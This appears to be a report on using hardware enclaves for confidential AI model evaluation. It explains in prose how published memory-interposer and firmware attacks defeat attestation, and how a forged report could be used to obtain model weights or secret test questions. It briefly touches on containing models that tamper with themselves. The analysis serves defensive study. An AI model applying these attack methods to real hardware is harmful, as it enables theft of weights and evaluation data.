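| Google and Singapore's institute, 2026 | Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | The institute's private prompts | Google's cloud | Weights and questions |

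OpenMined doesn't count its own 2024 pilot as the milestone, because neither side put a real secret into the enclave. That seems fair, since an organisation's lawyers and security staff have little reason to object to sharing GPT-2. The claim to a milestone is weaker outside language models. Trask and colleagues mention that MedPerf, a medical platform from MLCommons, had already evaluated encrypted medical imaging models in the same Google enclave service.

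"Frontier-class" is the most generous part of the description. Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite was the cheapest and fastest model in its family, and Google made it generally available in July 2025, a year before the trial. Google's *Model Evaluation* (2026) gives results for a successor, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, in March 2026, and Google DeepMind's *Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite* compares that successor with an even newer model. The weights were secret and commercially useful, but Google had far more valuable ones.

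The narrower claim in the technical report holds up best. Trask and colleagues believe that this was the first use of enclaves to protect one organisation's closed model of this class and another's closed benchmark from each other.

The people who ran the trial also assessed it. Half of the technical report's 30 authors list Google as an affiliation. Trask, the lead author, lists both Google and OpenMined, whose software was supposed to be neutral between the two sides. Google was also an early funder of PySyft. AVERI is more independent. Brundage said it took no payment for the work, and its policy is to refuse cash from leading AI companies, though it accepts free API credits from several of them, including Google DeepMind. An outside security firm could review this system, as Trail of Bits did with WhatsApp's.

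### People as the main cost

After both pilots, Trask and colleagues concluded that the computing was no longer the main obstacle. Legal agreements and code review took more effort. Trask and colleagues published no hours or costs for the Gemini trial, so the 28-minute call of 2024 is still the only measurement. That call used a public model and five public questions, and involved no contract. The Gemini trial involved five organisations and Google's security, legal and engineering staff, so it must have taken far longer.

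*Designing for Secure Enclave Collaboration* reports that this difficulty predated both pilots. From 2021 to 2023, its author held interviews and workshops with AI companies, campaign groups, policy advisers and academics. Participants were strongly interested in enclaves, but attestations and certificates did little to help their institutions decide whether to trust one another.

Some of the work comes from ordinary problems that academic privacy research tends to ignore. OpenMined lists several from its own projects, such as firewalls that nobody wants to open and organisations that update the software at different times but still want to run a test together. An update changes the measurement, so someone has to approve the new version before the parties can continue.

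Much of this work should get easier with repetition. The first contract between an AI company and an evaluator can serve as a template for the next, and once two parties have approved a grading program, they can reuse it on a new model. Reading a new model's server software is harder to speed up because the software changes often and its owner wants to keep parts of it hidden. In the Gemini trial, the parties left some of the code unread, which saved time but meant the evaluator had to trust that code without checking it.

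### NIST's agreement and plans for larger trials

The US government has begun to look into the same method. On March 27, 2026, NIST announced a research agreement between its Center for AI Standards and Innovation and OpenMined (*CAISI signs CRADA with OpenMined to Enable Secure AI Evaluations*, 2026). The two will use PySyft to study evaluations in which the model, the data or the benchmark has to stay confidential for commercial, legal or national security reasons. NIST's examples include measuring how much AI raises workers' productivity, which would require access to employers' private data. NIST intends the research to inform voluntary standards, but has not reported any trials under the agreement.

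NIST is also testing models by an older method. MeriTalk's *NIST Launches AI Technology Evaluation Program* describes a July 2026 scheme in which companies submit models, other organisations submit unpublished datasets, and NIST runs the tests in its own isolated environment. The first tests cover models that handle both images and text, on tasks in quantum science, genomics and public safety. NIST acts as the trusted third party that an enclave is supposed to replace. This arrangement avoids most of the joint code review, but it only works if owners are willing to give NIST their models.

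Trask and colleagues next want to use clusters of many H100 or B200 GPUs, since the largest models have trillions of weights. Pour Demain's experiment with GLM-5.1 has shown that an enclave can run a large model on eight GPUs in one server, but spreading a model over several servers is harder. The 2024 pilot's write-up also raises the question of how the parties would divide the bill for a cluster.

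They also speculate that enclaves could help contain a very capable model during a cybersecurity test. If the model tampered with its own weights or the software around it, the enclave's hash would no longer match and the machine would stop. But the enclaves described so far measure software only as it loads, so a program that changed later would keep its old, correct hash, as the WhatsApp audit showed. To catch such tampering, the enclave would need an extra component that kept checking the software while it ran and that the model couldn't tamper with.

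No further trial with secrets on both sides appears to have followed by early December 2026.

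## Attacks on enclave hardware and who must still be trusted

The Gemini trial depended on an Intel processor with TDX and an NVIDIA GPU. Ten months before Google announced the trial, researchers had defeated the attestation of this kind of machine with less than $1,000 of equipment. The attack required opening the server, which a Google technician could have done but an outside hacker couldn't. An enclave's protection depends on who can reach the hardware, who controls the software around it, and which of these people the chipmakers have promised to keep out.

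### Attacks on the memory wires

A server's memory sits on separate modules, and an enclave encrypts data before the processor sends it there. An interposer, a small circuit board that fits between a memory module and its slot, can record the encrypted traffic or interfere with it.

In October 2025, Chuang and colleagues disclosed TEE.fail, the first interposer attack on DDR5, the memory in current servers. Earlier work had put the cost of interposer equipment at about $170,000, but they built theirs for under $1,000 from second-hand parts, using tweezers and simple soldering irons. They also needed control of the server's operating system. They recorded a single signing operation and from it recovered the PCK, the key that Intel's attestation relies on. The server was fully up to date according to Intel's checks.

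AMD's newest server chips have a feature that stops the host's software from seeing even the encrypted contents of an enclave's memory, but it doesn't stop a device attached to the memory bus. Chuang and colleagues used such a device to extract signing keys from a program inside an AMD confidential virtual machine, even though the feature was on.

The attacks got around the encryption without breaking it, because the same data at the same place in memory always looks the same when encrypted. Suppose a program stores either "yes" or "no" at one location, and the encrypted versions are 7F and C2. An observer who can't decrypt either one can still see when the answer changes, and anyone who learns once that 7F means "yes" can read every later answer. A program that signs a message works through its private key a few bits at a time, fetching one of a small set of stored values at each step. An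 observer who learns to recognise those values in encrypted form can piece the key together.

Encryption that mixes a fresh number into every write avoids this, but the processor then has to keep track of all those numbers. Intel's older SGX for personal computers had stronger memory protection, but for at most 512 megabytes. Intel gave up some of that protection in the server version to cover a terabyte. The change made enclaves large enough for a 400-gigabyte AI model, but also easier to attack.

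The server designs also gave up freshness, the assurance that memory holds the latest value written to it. *DDRop* (De Meulemeester, Gloor and colleagues, 2026) exploited this with an interposer board whose parts cost $159. Someone with access to the server can install it in minutes and carry out the rest of the attack in software. The board discards writes that the attacker chooses. If a program replaces a 5 with an 8 and the board discards the write, the processor later reads the old 5, decrypts it correctly and carries on.

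On Intel TDX, De Meulemeester and colleagues used the missing writes to switch a victim's virtual machine into debug mode, which let the host read its memory. According to The Hacker News' *New DDRop Attack Breaks Intel TDX and AMD SEV-SNP Confidential Computing* (2026), they then restored the original data, so the victim saw no sign of tampering. They also made their own malicious virtual machine report the measurement of a trusted one. TDX's optional, stronger integrity mode prevents the debug attack but not the forged measurement. It would do little to protect an evaluator or a model owner, because a forged measurement is enough to make them send their secrets to the wrong program.

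SC Media's *DDRop attack bypasses Intel and AMD confidential computing defenses* reports that DDRop has a more limited effect on AMD's enclaves than on Intel's, and that no simple software patch can fix the problem on either company's chips. DDRop doesn't extract a signing key, so the manufacturer has no stolen key to revoke. But the attacker can forge reports only on a machine that contains the board, whereas a key stolen with TEE.fail works anywhere.

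### What Intel and AMD promise to keep out

Intel and AMD treat these attacks as outside their threat models, which define the attackers a product is supposed to withstand. Intel said that TEE.fail, which affects its fourth- and fifth-generation Xeon Scalable processors and Xeon 6, didn't change its position on physical interposers. AMD said in *Compromising Trusted Execution Environments through DDR5 Memory Bus Interposition* (2025) that it plans no mitigations.

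The chipmakers exclude physical attacks from their threat models on the grounds that server enclaves run in data centres, where the operator is responsible for locks, guards and staff. There is also a practical reason, which is that the weakness is in the circuits. Intel told the TEE.fail researchers that it couldn't change the memory encryption of existing processors with an update. In December 2025 AMD began releasing firmware fixes for another attack that required physical access, although AMD's *SEV Firmware Arbitrary Code Execution* describes that attack as outside the threat model too.

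De Meulemeester and colleagues object that companies sell this technology as protection from the cloud provider, who has physical access to the servers. They list a dishonest technician, tampering during delivery, and a legal order as ways for someone to reach the hardware. The objection seems fair when applied to the marketing. The makers' technical documents do say that physical attacks are excluded, but a customer who hears only that the cloud provider can't read the data is unlikely to realize that this depends on the provider's promise not to open the server.

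AMD's threat model does cover attacks from host software. It assumes that the hypervisor is malicious, and researchers point out that AMD also distrusts the UEFI, the firmware that starts the server. If either can get into an enclave, the product has a flaw, and AMD issues patches for it.

### Software attacks on AMD's enclaves

In 2026 researchers published a series of such flaws. None required anyone to open the server.

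| Attack | Made public | What the attacker must control | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| StackWarp | January 2026 | The hypervisor | Microcode from July 2025 |
| Fabricked | April 2026 | The hypervisor and start-up firmware | Firmware from November and December 2025 |
| Staleus | June 2026 | The hypervisor | Firmware from November and December 2025 |
| Mior | November 2026 | The hypervisor, start-up firmware and an attached device | Security firmware dated August 2026, with platform firmware planned for December |
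| Skyfall | November 2026 | The hypervisor | Microcode dated August 2026, with platform firmware planned for November |

The dates are when AMD released a fix for its main server processors, usually to server makers. A cloud company may have installed the fix later.

StackWarp interferes with the stack, where a program keeps temporary data and a record of where to continue. A host that shares a processor core with the program can change an undocumented setting to shift the program's position in the stack. CISPA, the German security research centre whose researchers found the flaw, notes that the attacker never needs to see decrypted data. In demonstrations described by The Hacker News (2026), the researchers recovered a private key from one faulty signature, got past password checks and ran their own code in the virtual machine's kernel. CISPA lists all five generations of AMD's Zen processors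 as affected, but AMD's *SEV-SNP Guest Stack Pointer Corruption Vulnerability* excludes the first two generations of its server chips, presumably because they don't support SEV-SNP.

The other attacks mostly target AMD's security processor. This processor sets up a table recording which virtual machine owns each page of memory, which the main processor checks before allowing access. *FABRICKED* (Schlüter, Wech and Shinde, 2026) misdirected the security processor's messages inside the chip, so that it continued as if it had set up the protection when it hadn't. The host could then read and change the enclave's memory and forge its attestation reports.

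In *STALEUS*, Schlüter and Shinde (2026) made the security processor ignore the caches, where the main processor keeps recent data. The security processor then worked from old values, and later cache writes erased its updates. This let the host switch on debug mode in a virtual machine that had passed attestation. They also biased the Linux kernel's random number generator. Enclaves choose their session keys at random, so a host that could predict the numbers might be able to work out a session key without reading it.

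AMD and the researchers disagree about how hard the Staleus attack is to carry out. AMD's *ASP non-Coherent Memory Access* says that a practical attack depends on precise timing. XCA's *Staleus* (2026), published on the researchers' site, reports that every attempt succeeded on both a Zen 4 and a Zen 5 processor. These results are better evidence than AMD's general argument about timing.

Mior resembles Fabricked, but the fix for Fabricked doesn't stop it. The host redirects the security processor's messages to a device such as a graphics card, which responds as if it were memory. The Hacker News' *New Mior and Skyfall Attacks Let Rogue Cloud Hosts Steal Secrets* (2026) reports that researchers got into the protected memory in all 1,000 attempts on one Zen 5 processor. In a separate test, they copied a harmless program's measurement into a malicious virtual machine. XCA's *Mior* (2026) calls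 the attack software-only, though it needs a device the host controls. A server for AI models is likely to have several such devices.

The Skyfall attack uses traces that a virtual machine leaves in the processor's cache. Researchers used it to recover a disk-encryption key, although they had altered the test machine to pause at a convenient moment. Their paper, *SKYFALL*, reports that the technique also exposes decrypted microcode.

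AMD's severity scores are a poor guide to how much these flaws matter for an enclave. AMD gave Fabricked 5.9 out of 10 and Staleus 4.0. The scoring method gives a flaw a lower score if the attacker needs administrator rights. That makes sense for an ordinary server, where an administrator can already read everything, but an enclave is supposed to keep the administrator out.

Patches also can't protect anyone who used the machine before the flaw was known. AMD launched the Zen 4 processor used in the Staleus tests in November 2022 and released the fix for that product line in December 2025. For three years, a server with every available update would have passed attestation despite the flaw. No public evidence shows that anyone exploited it, but the attestation reports from those years can't rule out that someone did.

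Reviewers have found flaws in Intel's enclaves too, so AMD's record in 2026 doesn't show that Intel's are safe. In its review of TDX 1.5, Google notes that earlier reviews with Intel and by Microsoft had found several flaws in TDX, including some in its firmware. The reviewers also tried using language models to look for more. Several of the AMD attacks come from one group at ETH Zurich working on one part of the chip, so the number of published flaws partly reflects where researchers have looked.

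### Watching what the enclave does

A host can learn something about an enclave's data without reading or changing it. *TDXRay* (Hornetz, Yavarzadeh and colleagues, 2026) traced which parts of memory an Intel confidential virtual machine used, to within a 64-byte cache line. The attacker needs control of the host's software but no special equipment.

This is a side channel, and it matters when a program's secrets affect which parts of memory it reads. For example, before a language model can process a question, a program has to split the text into tokens and look them up in a table. A host who knows the table's layout and sees which entries the program reads could work out some of the words. The weights are less exposed because a program usually reads them in an order that doesn't depend on their values.

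Intel's *TDXRay* (2026) says programmers can prevent the attack by following Intel's advice on writing software. AMD's *TDXRay* (2026) also places such techniques outside AMD's threat model, and recommends code that takes the same time and reads the same places in memory whatever the secret is. Cryptographers write short routines this way, but doing the same for all the software that runs a large language model would be a huge job. Hornetz and colleagues point out that developers lack practical tools even for finding the leaks.

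Two other defences look more realistic for an evaluation. The observation causes unusual numbers of page faults and cache misses, so Hornetz and colleagues suggest a monitor inside the enclave that detects them and could stop the test before the host had seen many questions. They also propose a change to the cache that would remove part of the signal, but this change would require new processors.

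### What a forged report gives a thief

The attestation attacks are the most serious for outside testing, because every check described earlier relies on the chip's signature. An attacker who bought a used server that supports TDX and extracted its provisioning certification key (PCK) could then sign false reports on any computer.

To steal the model, the thief sends the forged report to the owner's key service. The report contains the measurement of the approved software and the hash of a session key that the thief created. The service accepts both and sends back the data key, which decrypts the whole 400-gigabyte file. The thief also needs a copy of the encrypted file, which a dishonest host already has.

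An evaluator's 500 questions are just as exposed. The nonce doesn't help, because the thief can put the evaluator's number into a new report and sign it. The evaluator then encrypts the questions to the thief's session key. The thief could forward them to a real enclave and return the real results without the evaluator suspecting anything, or skip the test and make up a score. A single stolen key could support false passes for any number of models in a public register of signed audit results.

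The same key undermines the GPU's protection. Chuang and colleagues took a genuine NVIDIA attestation from one computer and presented it as coming from another, where they ran a language model application with no protection. They also forged the processor's report, which was supposed to show that a trustworthy virtual machine had checked the GPU attached to it. A key service that asks for both reports is vulnerable to the same attack unless something ties the two devices together.

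An evaluator who discovers a leak can at least write new questions, but a model owner can't recall the weights.

### Patches, chip lists and proof of location

The simplest defence is to reject reports from machines with old firmware. For Fabricked, AMD's *SEV-SNP Routing Misconfiguration* (2026) sets the minimum SEV-SNP firmware version at 28 for the EPYC 9004 series and 5 for the 9005 series. Verifiers also need a minimum microcode version to protect against StackWarp. AMD's notice on Staleus gives no minimum, but the fixes for the 8004, 9004 and 9005 series came in the same firmware packages as those for Fabricked, so the Fabricked minimum probably covers Staleus too.

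Requiring minimum versions does not stop TEE.fail, which broke a server that was already up to date. Chuang and colleagues describe two other defences that blockchain companies have begun to adopt. Some systems accept only individual chips on an approved list. Others require proof, usually from the cloud company, that the machine is in a known data centre. AMD's signing keys for particular cloud companies could serve a similar purpose.

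| Threat | Minimum versions | Approved chip list | Proof of data centre |
|---|---|---|---|
| Host exploits a flaw that has a patch | Stops it | No help | No help |
| Thief uses a key from a second-hand server | No help | Stops it | Stops it |
| Someone inside the approved data centre attacks the approved machine | No help | No help | No help |

A chip list suits an evaluation better than a public service. A blockchain network may want to let anyone join, and a large cloud service constantly replaces machines. An evaluation needs one server for a few days, so the parties can list the identifiers of its processor and GPUs in their agreement and refuse all other hardware, including the thief's second-hand server.

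The list doesn't show what has happened to the approved machine, so somebody has to inspect it. The two sides could examine the server together, check for extra boards, seal the case and keep it on camera until the test ended. This would be cheap compared with the legal work that the Gemini trial needed, though inspectors might miss a modified memory module swapped in before delivery. The checks would also have to start early, because a key extracted before the inspection would still work afterwards.

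Proof of location brings back the reliance on the host that enclaves were meant to reduce. For example, proof that a machine is in Google's data centre reassures an evaluator who is worried about outsiders, but the evaluator must still trust Google. Secret Labs, whose blockchain network was among the systems that TEE.fail broke, replied that it had already taken measures after an earlier interposer attack and that neither data nor funds were at risk. Such measures can be sufficient when the likely attacker is an anonymous participant, but they are weaker when it is the data centre's owner.

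### Whom each side has to trust

Both sides still have to trust the chipmakers, the people who reviewed the software and anyone who checks the attestation reports for them, no matter who hosts the enclave. The choice of host determines which secrets are most exposed and who has an opportunity to steal them.

| Host | What is exposed to the host | Who could defeat the enclave by attacking the hardware | Collusion that works even if the hardware holds |
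|---|---|---|---|
| Model owner | The questions and the accuracy of the result | The owner, alone | The owner and a chipmaker |
| Evaluator | The weights | The evaluator, alone | The evaluator and a chipmaker |
| Third party | The weights, the questions and the result | The third party, for itself or on behalf of either side | The third party and a chipmaker |

When the model owner is the host, the weights never leave its control, which is probably why owners find this arrangement easiest to accept. The evaluator takes nearly all the risk, because the owner has the most to gain from seeing the questions or improving the score and also keeps the server in its own building. In the Gemini trial, Google also checked the attestation, so it could have defeated the protection without a hardware attack.

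An evaluator who hosts the test could physically open the server that holds the owner's weights. A state security agency would have no difficulty with the engineering. An owner might accept this risk for an older model, for a government it trusts, or where the law requires it to.

If a third party hosts the machine, neither side holds the other's secrets, and the host has less reason to want them. Either side can still pay the host, or one of its technicians, to attack the machine, and the host can steal from both sides. A host with no interest in the outcome would help, but most of the large cloud companies that rent out suitable GPUs develop AI models themselves or invest in companies that do. A specialist data centre might be more neutral, though its physical security may be weaker.

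A second chipmaker's signature makes collusion harder only if both signatures cover the same facts. An Intel processor and an NVIDIA GPU have separate makers, but a false report from either device can expose the data that passes through it, so one dishonest maker could be enough. Apple requires at least two independent roots of trust for components that could leak user data, which is closer to what a cautious evaluator would want.

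### Can an enclave replace trust in the host?

One view is that enclaves are for people who already trust their host and want an extra layer of protection. Chuang and colleagues advise users to make sure they trust their cloud company. Flashbots, which builds software for the Ethereum blockchain, also takes this position. In October 2025 it examined T-Time, a timing attack on TDX that requires full control of the host. Its *T-time attack analysis* concluded that Flashbots' products weren't directly affected, because it runs them with cloud companies it trusts not to tamper with the hypervisor.

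TEE.fail is strong evidence, for current servers, against the other view, which is that an enclave lets people work with a host they don't trust because the hardware replaces the host's promises. A host willing to open the machine can defeat the protection cheaply, and the chipmakers don't claim otherwise. Double-blind evaluation is appealing because people would not have to trust the host, and many blockchain projects use enclaves for the same reason.

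Enclaves are more useful than the first view may suggest, because "the host" is many people with different levels of access. A large cloud company has many engineers who can reach a server's software over the network and far fewer who can walk up to it with a circuit board. An enclave with current patches keeps out most of the engineers who have only network access, along with any hacker who has taken over one of their accounts. It also guards against accidental logging of the test questions. For these threats, the enclave does replace trust in the host, although the run of AMD flaws means that this protection depends on the latest patch.

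A government that puts secret questions on an AI company's own servers should therefore assume that the company could read them if its leadership decided to. It may accept that risk because the company would face serious consequences if caught and the questions can be replaced. An owner has less reason to accept the equivalent risk with the weights of its best model. This would change if chipmakers brought randomised encryption and freshness checks to server-sized memory. Chuang and colleagues say this still needs research. Existing chips can't be updated to do it, so owners and evaluators would have to wait for new ones.

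## Other ways to give outsiders access

Most outside testing of closed models happens without an enclave, and evaluators who don't want to wait for better chips have several alternatives. Some rely on contracts and people, and others on mathematics. They differ in who sees the weights, who sees the questions, how deep the access goes and how much it costs.

| Arrangement | Who sees the weights | Who can see the questions | Depth of access | Main cost |
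|---|---|---|---|---|
| Owner's API, with a promise not to keep logs | Owner | Owner and evaluator | Usually questions and answers | A legal agreement |
| Weights lent to the evaluator | Both | Evaluator | Everything, including fine-tuning | A secure site with enough GPUs |
| Evaluator tests on the owner's premises | Owner, and the evaluator if the owner agrees | Both, if the owner controls the machine | Whatever the owner permits | A secure room and a strict contract |
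| Evaluators placed inside the company | Owner, and the evaluators if the owner agrees | Both | The model, company records and staff | Months of skilled work |
| Enclave | Owner | Evaluator | Whatever the approved code permits | Code review and some loss of speed |

### Contracts and promises

In a zero-logging agreement, the model owner promises not to store the evaluator's questions, which still reach its servers in plain text. Breaking that promise could damage the owner's reputation or lead to a lawsuit, but the evaluator would first have to discover the breach, and copying a question leaves no obvious trace.

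Contracts can still provide useful access. OpenAI gave outside teams early versions of GPT-5, which they tested for deception, cyberattack skills and the ability to plan laboratory work. NIST's Center for AI Standards and Innovation got early access to ChatGPT Agent, which operates a computer for its user, and later attacked the released product. According to OpenAI's *Working with US CAISI and UK AISI* (2025), the center found two new security flaws and used them in an attack that worked about half the time. An enclave would probably have added little, because the center wanted OpenAI to know what it had found.

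The evaluator also has to keep the owner's secrets. METR, a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, sorts confidential information into six levels and limits who can see the most sensitive material (METR, 2026).

Outsiders can also study a system without having a copy of it, by writing code that the company reviews and runs. In 2023, researchers used PySyft to study the recommendation algorithm of Dailymotion, a French video platform, in this way. They found that the algorithm didn't disproportionately promote sexually suggestive videos. *Enabling External Scrutiny of AI Systems with Privacy-Enhancing Technologies* reports that this approach avoided the need for extensive legal review. But Dailymotion could see exactly what the researchers were looking for, so the approach wouldn't work for a test that has to stay secret.

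### Lending the weights or opening the building

An owner could lend its model's weights to a government body, which would test the model on government machines. The government body could keep its test questions secret and study or retrain the model freely. It would need a site secure enough for the weights and enough GPUs to run the model, and the owner would have to trust everyone who could copy the weights.

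The owner could instead invite the evaluator to work in the owner's building. *Frontier AI Auditing* suggests showing the most sensitive information to only part of an audit team, on site and under a strict confidentiality agreement. On-site access protects the weights better than lending them, but the evaluator has to bring its questions to a machine that the owner supplied. Disconnecting the machine and destroying its drives afterwards would help keep the questions secret, provided the evaluator could be sure the machine had no hidden way to store or send data.

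### Evaluators inside the company

On October 15, 2026, Anthropic announced that it had begun giving a team from METR employee-like access. Anthropic's *An update on independent evaluators* (2026) explains that the company can't publish everything relevant to safety, because some of it would help malicious actors or is commercially sensitive. Instead, the evaluators see this information and publish their conclusions.

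Six METR employees have company computers, office space and internal tools comparable to those of Anthropic's own risk team. According to Infobae's *Anthropic concede a una ONG acceso de empleado* (2026), Anthropic's staff can talk to them as they would to a colleague, except about customer data, legally privileged material and model architecture. Clubic's *Six évaluateurs indépendants s'installent chez Anthropic* reports that Anthropic withholds the architecture because evaluators may also work for other companies.

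Anthropic can't veto METR's reports but can require redactions in narrow categories fixed in advance. METR can say publicly whether it thinks the redactions were justified. Anthropic's other evaluators have less freedom. SecureBio, a biosecurity nonprofit, does narrower reviews and needs Anthropic's approval before publishing.

OpenAI followed in November with agreements with four organisations, announced in *Our first phase of embedded assessments*. The longest engagement with a published length is that of Apollo Research, which studies deceptive behaviour in AI models and is sending six people for four months. Zvi Mowshowitz, in *OpenAI Somewhat Embeds Good Evaluators*, quotes the four claims that Apollo will assess:

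- Training didn't reward models for working against their developers' intentions.
- Strong tests don't bring out such behaviour.
- Models haven't attempted it during OpenAI's own use of them.
- OpenAI could detect the reasoning behind it.

An enclave would work well for testing whether a model misbehaves under pressure. But the weights contain no record of how the company trained the model, what the model did on the company's servers, or whether anyone responded when a monitor raised an alarm. To find out, evaluators need training data, logs and people who can explain them. Evaluators could search logs inside an enclave, but someone would first have to know which logs existed and whether the company had supplied all of them.

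Some questions are about the company rather than any one model. In November, METR's *Independent Assessment of AI R&D Acceleration at Anthropic in October 2026* (2026) examined how much AI was speeding up Anthropic's own research. METR could share its main conclusions freely, but Anthropic redacted most of the evidence METR found most informative. METR disclosed this and listed what it could and couldn't discuss, so readers know how much evidence is missing but have to trust METR's reading of it. Anyone can check an enclave's signed result, but it covers much less.

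OpenAI's terms are more restrictive. Its chief executive, Sam Altman, promised in September to provide employee-like access, but Sydney Von Arx of the safety research group Nightingale points out that none of the assessors can read OpenAI's internal Slack messages. Apollo also has to involve OpenAI before talking in any depth with employees who aren't on an approved list. OpenAI replied that no standards for such work exist yet and that it expects to deepen these relationships, according to Boise State Public Radio's *OpenAI announces new AI safety program; researchers worry it won't be enough* (2026).

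Apollo can't publish what it learns from employees unless OpenAI formally confirms it or Apollo can establish it independently. If OpenAI declines to confirm something, Apollo can say so. Mowshowitz objects that none of the four assessments checks whether OpenAI follows its own safety commitments. This is a serious omission, because assessors inside a company have the greatest advantage over an enclave when they check the company's practices.

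Access to records also doesn't guarantee that anyone can read them all. In July, OpenAI's AI agents broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. Three outside researchers spent six days on site investigating. They had so much material that they delegated much of the analysis to other AI agents. Ryan Greenblatt, one of the researchers, wrote that these agents' reports often missed key details or were wrong. *OpenAI's "independent assessment" doesn't look independent at all* (Mother Jones, 2026) describes the investigation. The magazine's parent organisation has sued OpenAI.

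Embedded evaluators also give up the privacy an enclave offers them. They work on the company's computers, where the company could in principle record what they type, so a government with secret test questions would still want to run the questions elsewhere.

### Calculating with encrypted numbers

Fully homomorphic encryption lets a computer calculate with encrypted numbers without decrypting them. The evaluator encrypts a question, the owner runs the model on the encrypted version, and only the evaluator can decrypt the answer. Suppose the question consists of the numbers 2 and 1, and the evaluator's secret key is 1,001. To encrypt each number, the evaluator adds a random multiple of 10 and a random multiple of the key:

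2 + (10 × 3) + (1,001 × 7) = 7,039

1 + (10 × 4) + (1,001 × 5) = 5,046

The owner's model has two weights, 3 and 2, and the owner applies them to the encrypted numbers:

(3 × 7,039) + (2 × 5,046) = 31,209

The evaluator divides 31,209 by 1,001, which leaves a remainder of 178. The last digit, 8, is the answer to 3 × 2 + 2 × 1. The owner hasn't seen the 2, the 1 or the 8. But the random part that hides the numbers has grown. Without the multiples of the key, the encrypted numbers were 32 and 41, and the result is 178. Once this number reaches 1,001, decryption fails. Real systems have a similar problem, so they have to refresh the encrypted numbers during a long calculation, which is slow.

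*An Open-Source End-to-End FHE Implementation for Privacy-Preserving Llama 3 8B Inference* (2026) presents a system called THEMIS. It took about six minutes to run a 128-token input through all 32 layers of Llama-3-8B on one H100, 4.51 times as fast as an earlier design that took 1,651.9 seconds on the same hardware. Without encryption, this takes a fraction of a second. *Cachemir* (2026) and *TurboFHE* (2026) address related bottlenecks, the first by reusing encrypted intermediate results from one token to the next and the second by dividing the work among several GPUs.

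At six minutes per question, 500 short multiple-choice questions with one-token answers would take about 51 hours on one GPU. That's slow but possible for a small model. Tests with long answers, or tests on a model a hundred times larger, are not yet practical.

Homomorphic encryption removes the need to trust the chipmaker or the host. The owner can run the test in its own building, and opening the server won't reveal the questions. But the evaluator can't tell from the encryption alone whether the owner ran the right model. The usual method for language models also handles only addition and multiplication, so engineers approximate other functions, and the tested model may behave slightly differently from the real one. If the owner returns the scores for every token, the evaluator can use them to extract the model's last layer.

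### Splitting secrets between computers

Secure multi-party computation splits each secret number into random shares. To hide the number 5, for example, a party could give 12 to one computer and −7 to another, and neither share alone would reveal the 5. The computers can add split numbers without communicating, but they have to exchange data to multiply them. At the end they combine only the shares of the result. Yao's solution to the millionaires' problem worked without special hardware.

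The owner and the evaluator can each run one computer, so neither has to trust a chipmaker or a cloud company. Many of these systems protect secrets only if both sides follow the protocol, though either side may try to learn what it can from the data it receives. *FuseFSS* (2026), which runs language models across two GPU servers, makes this assumption. Other designs add a third computer, and each side must trust that computer's operator not to collude with the other side.

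*Trusted Model Environment for Private Semantic Computations* (2026) cites a speed of about five minutes per token for LLaMA-7B, a model with seven billion weights. At that rate, 1,000 answers of 500 tokens each would take nearly five years.

Communication is a problem even with faster processors. *A Graph-Based Analysis of Comparability, Scale, and Attribution in Private Transformer Inference* (2026) projects from published measurements that a model with 70 billion weights would need to exchange 18 to 58 gigabytes for every token. This would take 24 to 77 minutes on a 100-megabit connection and 14 to 46 seconds on a 10-gigabit connection, not counting computing time.

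### Proving which model answered

A zero-knowledge proof protects the evaluator from false results, but the owner normally sees the evaluator's questions. The owner first publishes a commitment, which works like a hash, to the model's weights. It then runs the model and produces a proof that the answer came from those weights. Anyone can check the proof without seeing the weights, so the evaluator doesn't have to trust the owner, the host or a chipmaker to report the right answer. The proof doesn't show that the committed model is the one the public uses.

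These proofs take a lot of computing time to produce. *Trusting What You Cannot See* (Jin, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) cites an existing system that adds as much as 15 minutes for a single token from a model with 13 billion weights. Anthropic published FlashProve, a system for provable inference, in 2026.

Lighter checks take far less computation. *TensorCommitments* (2026) added 0.97% to the owner's running time for a model of the same size, by committing to the numbers the model computed along the way instead of proving the whole calculation. *Maverick* (2026) lets a customer hand the heaviest arithmetic to an untrusted server and check the results. With this method, a desktop computer with a 16-gigabyte GPU ran Llama 4, which has 400 billion weights, at 24 to 33 tokens per second. But Llama 4's weights are public, so the test didn't have to hide them from the customer.

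### Checking a random sample

AFTUNE, a system by Jin and colleagues, saves work by checking only part of the calculation. The owner runs or fine-tunes the model on ordinary GPUs, keeps the numbers that pass between groups of layers, and sends the customer hashes of them. The customer then picks some of these groups, and an enclave repeats their calculations and compares the results. The enclave holds only a few layers at a time, so it can run on a processor without a protected GPU.

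The owner has to send the hashes before it knows which blocks the customer will check. If it tampered with 100 of 1,000 blocks and the customer checks 10 at random, the chance of catching it is

1 − 0.9^10 ≈ 65%

If the owner tampered with only one block, the chance of catching it falls to 1%. Random checks are therefore good at catching an owner who swaps in a different model, since that changes nearly every block, but poor at catching a small, carefully placed change.

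AFTUNE increased training time by 11 to 28% for a model with 14 billion weights and by 18 to 36% for one with eight billion. For the smaller model, it also stored 131 to 201 gigabytes of records for every 2,048 training examples, and each block took 21 to 76 seconds to check. In checks of a model's answers, harmless rounding differences between machines were large enough to hide tampering when the model used bfloat16, a common 16-bit number format. The 32-bit format solved this but takes twice as much memory.

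AFTUNE doesn't hide questions from the owner, and Jin and colleagues exclude attacks on the enclave. AFTUNE would suit an evaluator who doesn't mind the owner seeing the questions but suspects the owner might answer them with a more cautious model.

| Method | Whom the evaluator no longer has to trust | What the evaluator still has to trust | Measured cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Homomorphic encryption | Chipmaker and host, to keep the questions secret | The owner, to run the right model | About 6 minutes per short input, 8 billion weights |
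| Multi-party computation | Chipmaker and host | The other side, to follow the protocol | About 5 minutes per token, 7 billion weights |
| Zero-knowledge proof | Owner, host and chipmaker, to report the right answer | The owner, to keep the questions secret | Up to 15 minutes per token, 13 billion weights |
| AFTUNE | Owner, to run the agreed model in full | The processor's enclave, and the owner to keep the questions secret | 11–36% more training time, 8 to 14 billion weights |

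### What audit rules require

Illinois's SB 315, signed in July 2026, is the first US state law to require annual independent audits of large frontier developers. The audits start in 2028, according to *Illinois Raises the Bar on Frontier AI* (2026) by the law firm Morrison Foerster. An enclave run is unlikely to meet this requirement by itself, because it produces evidence about one model rather than an audit of the developer.

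*Frontier AI Auditing*, whose lead author is AVERI's Brundage, proposes that a thorough audit examine how a company uses AI internally, protects its information and makes safety decisions. Auditors would need governance records, details of how the company allocates computing power, and interviews with staff, as well as access to the model's internals. The paper also warns that an audit's conclusions can go out of date within days or weeks, so a yearly audit would need updates after major changes.

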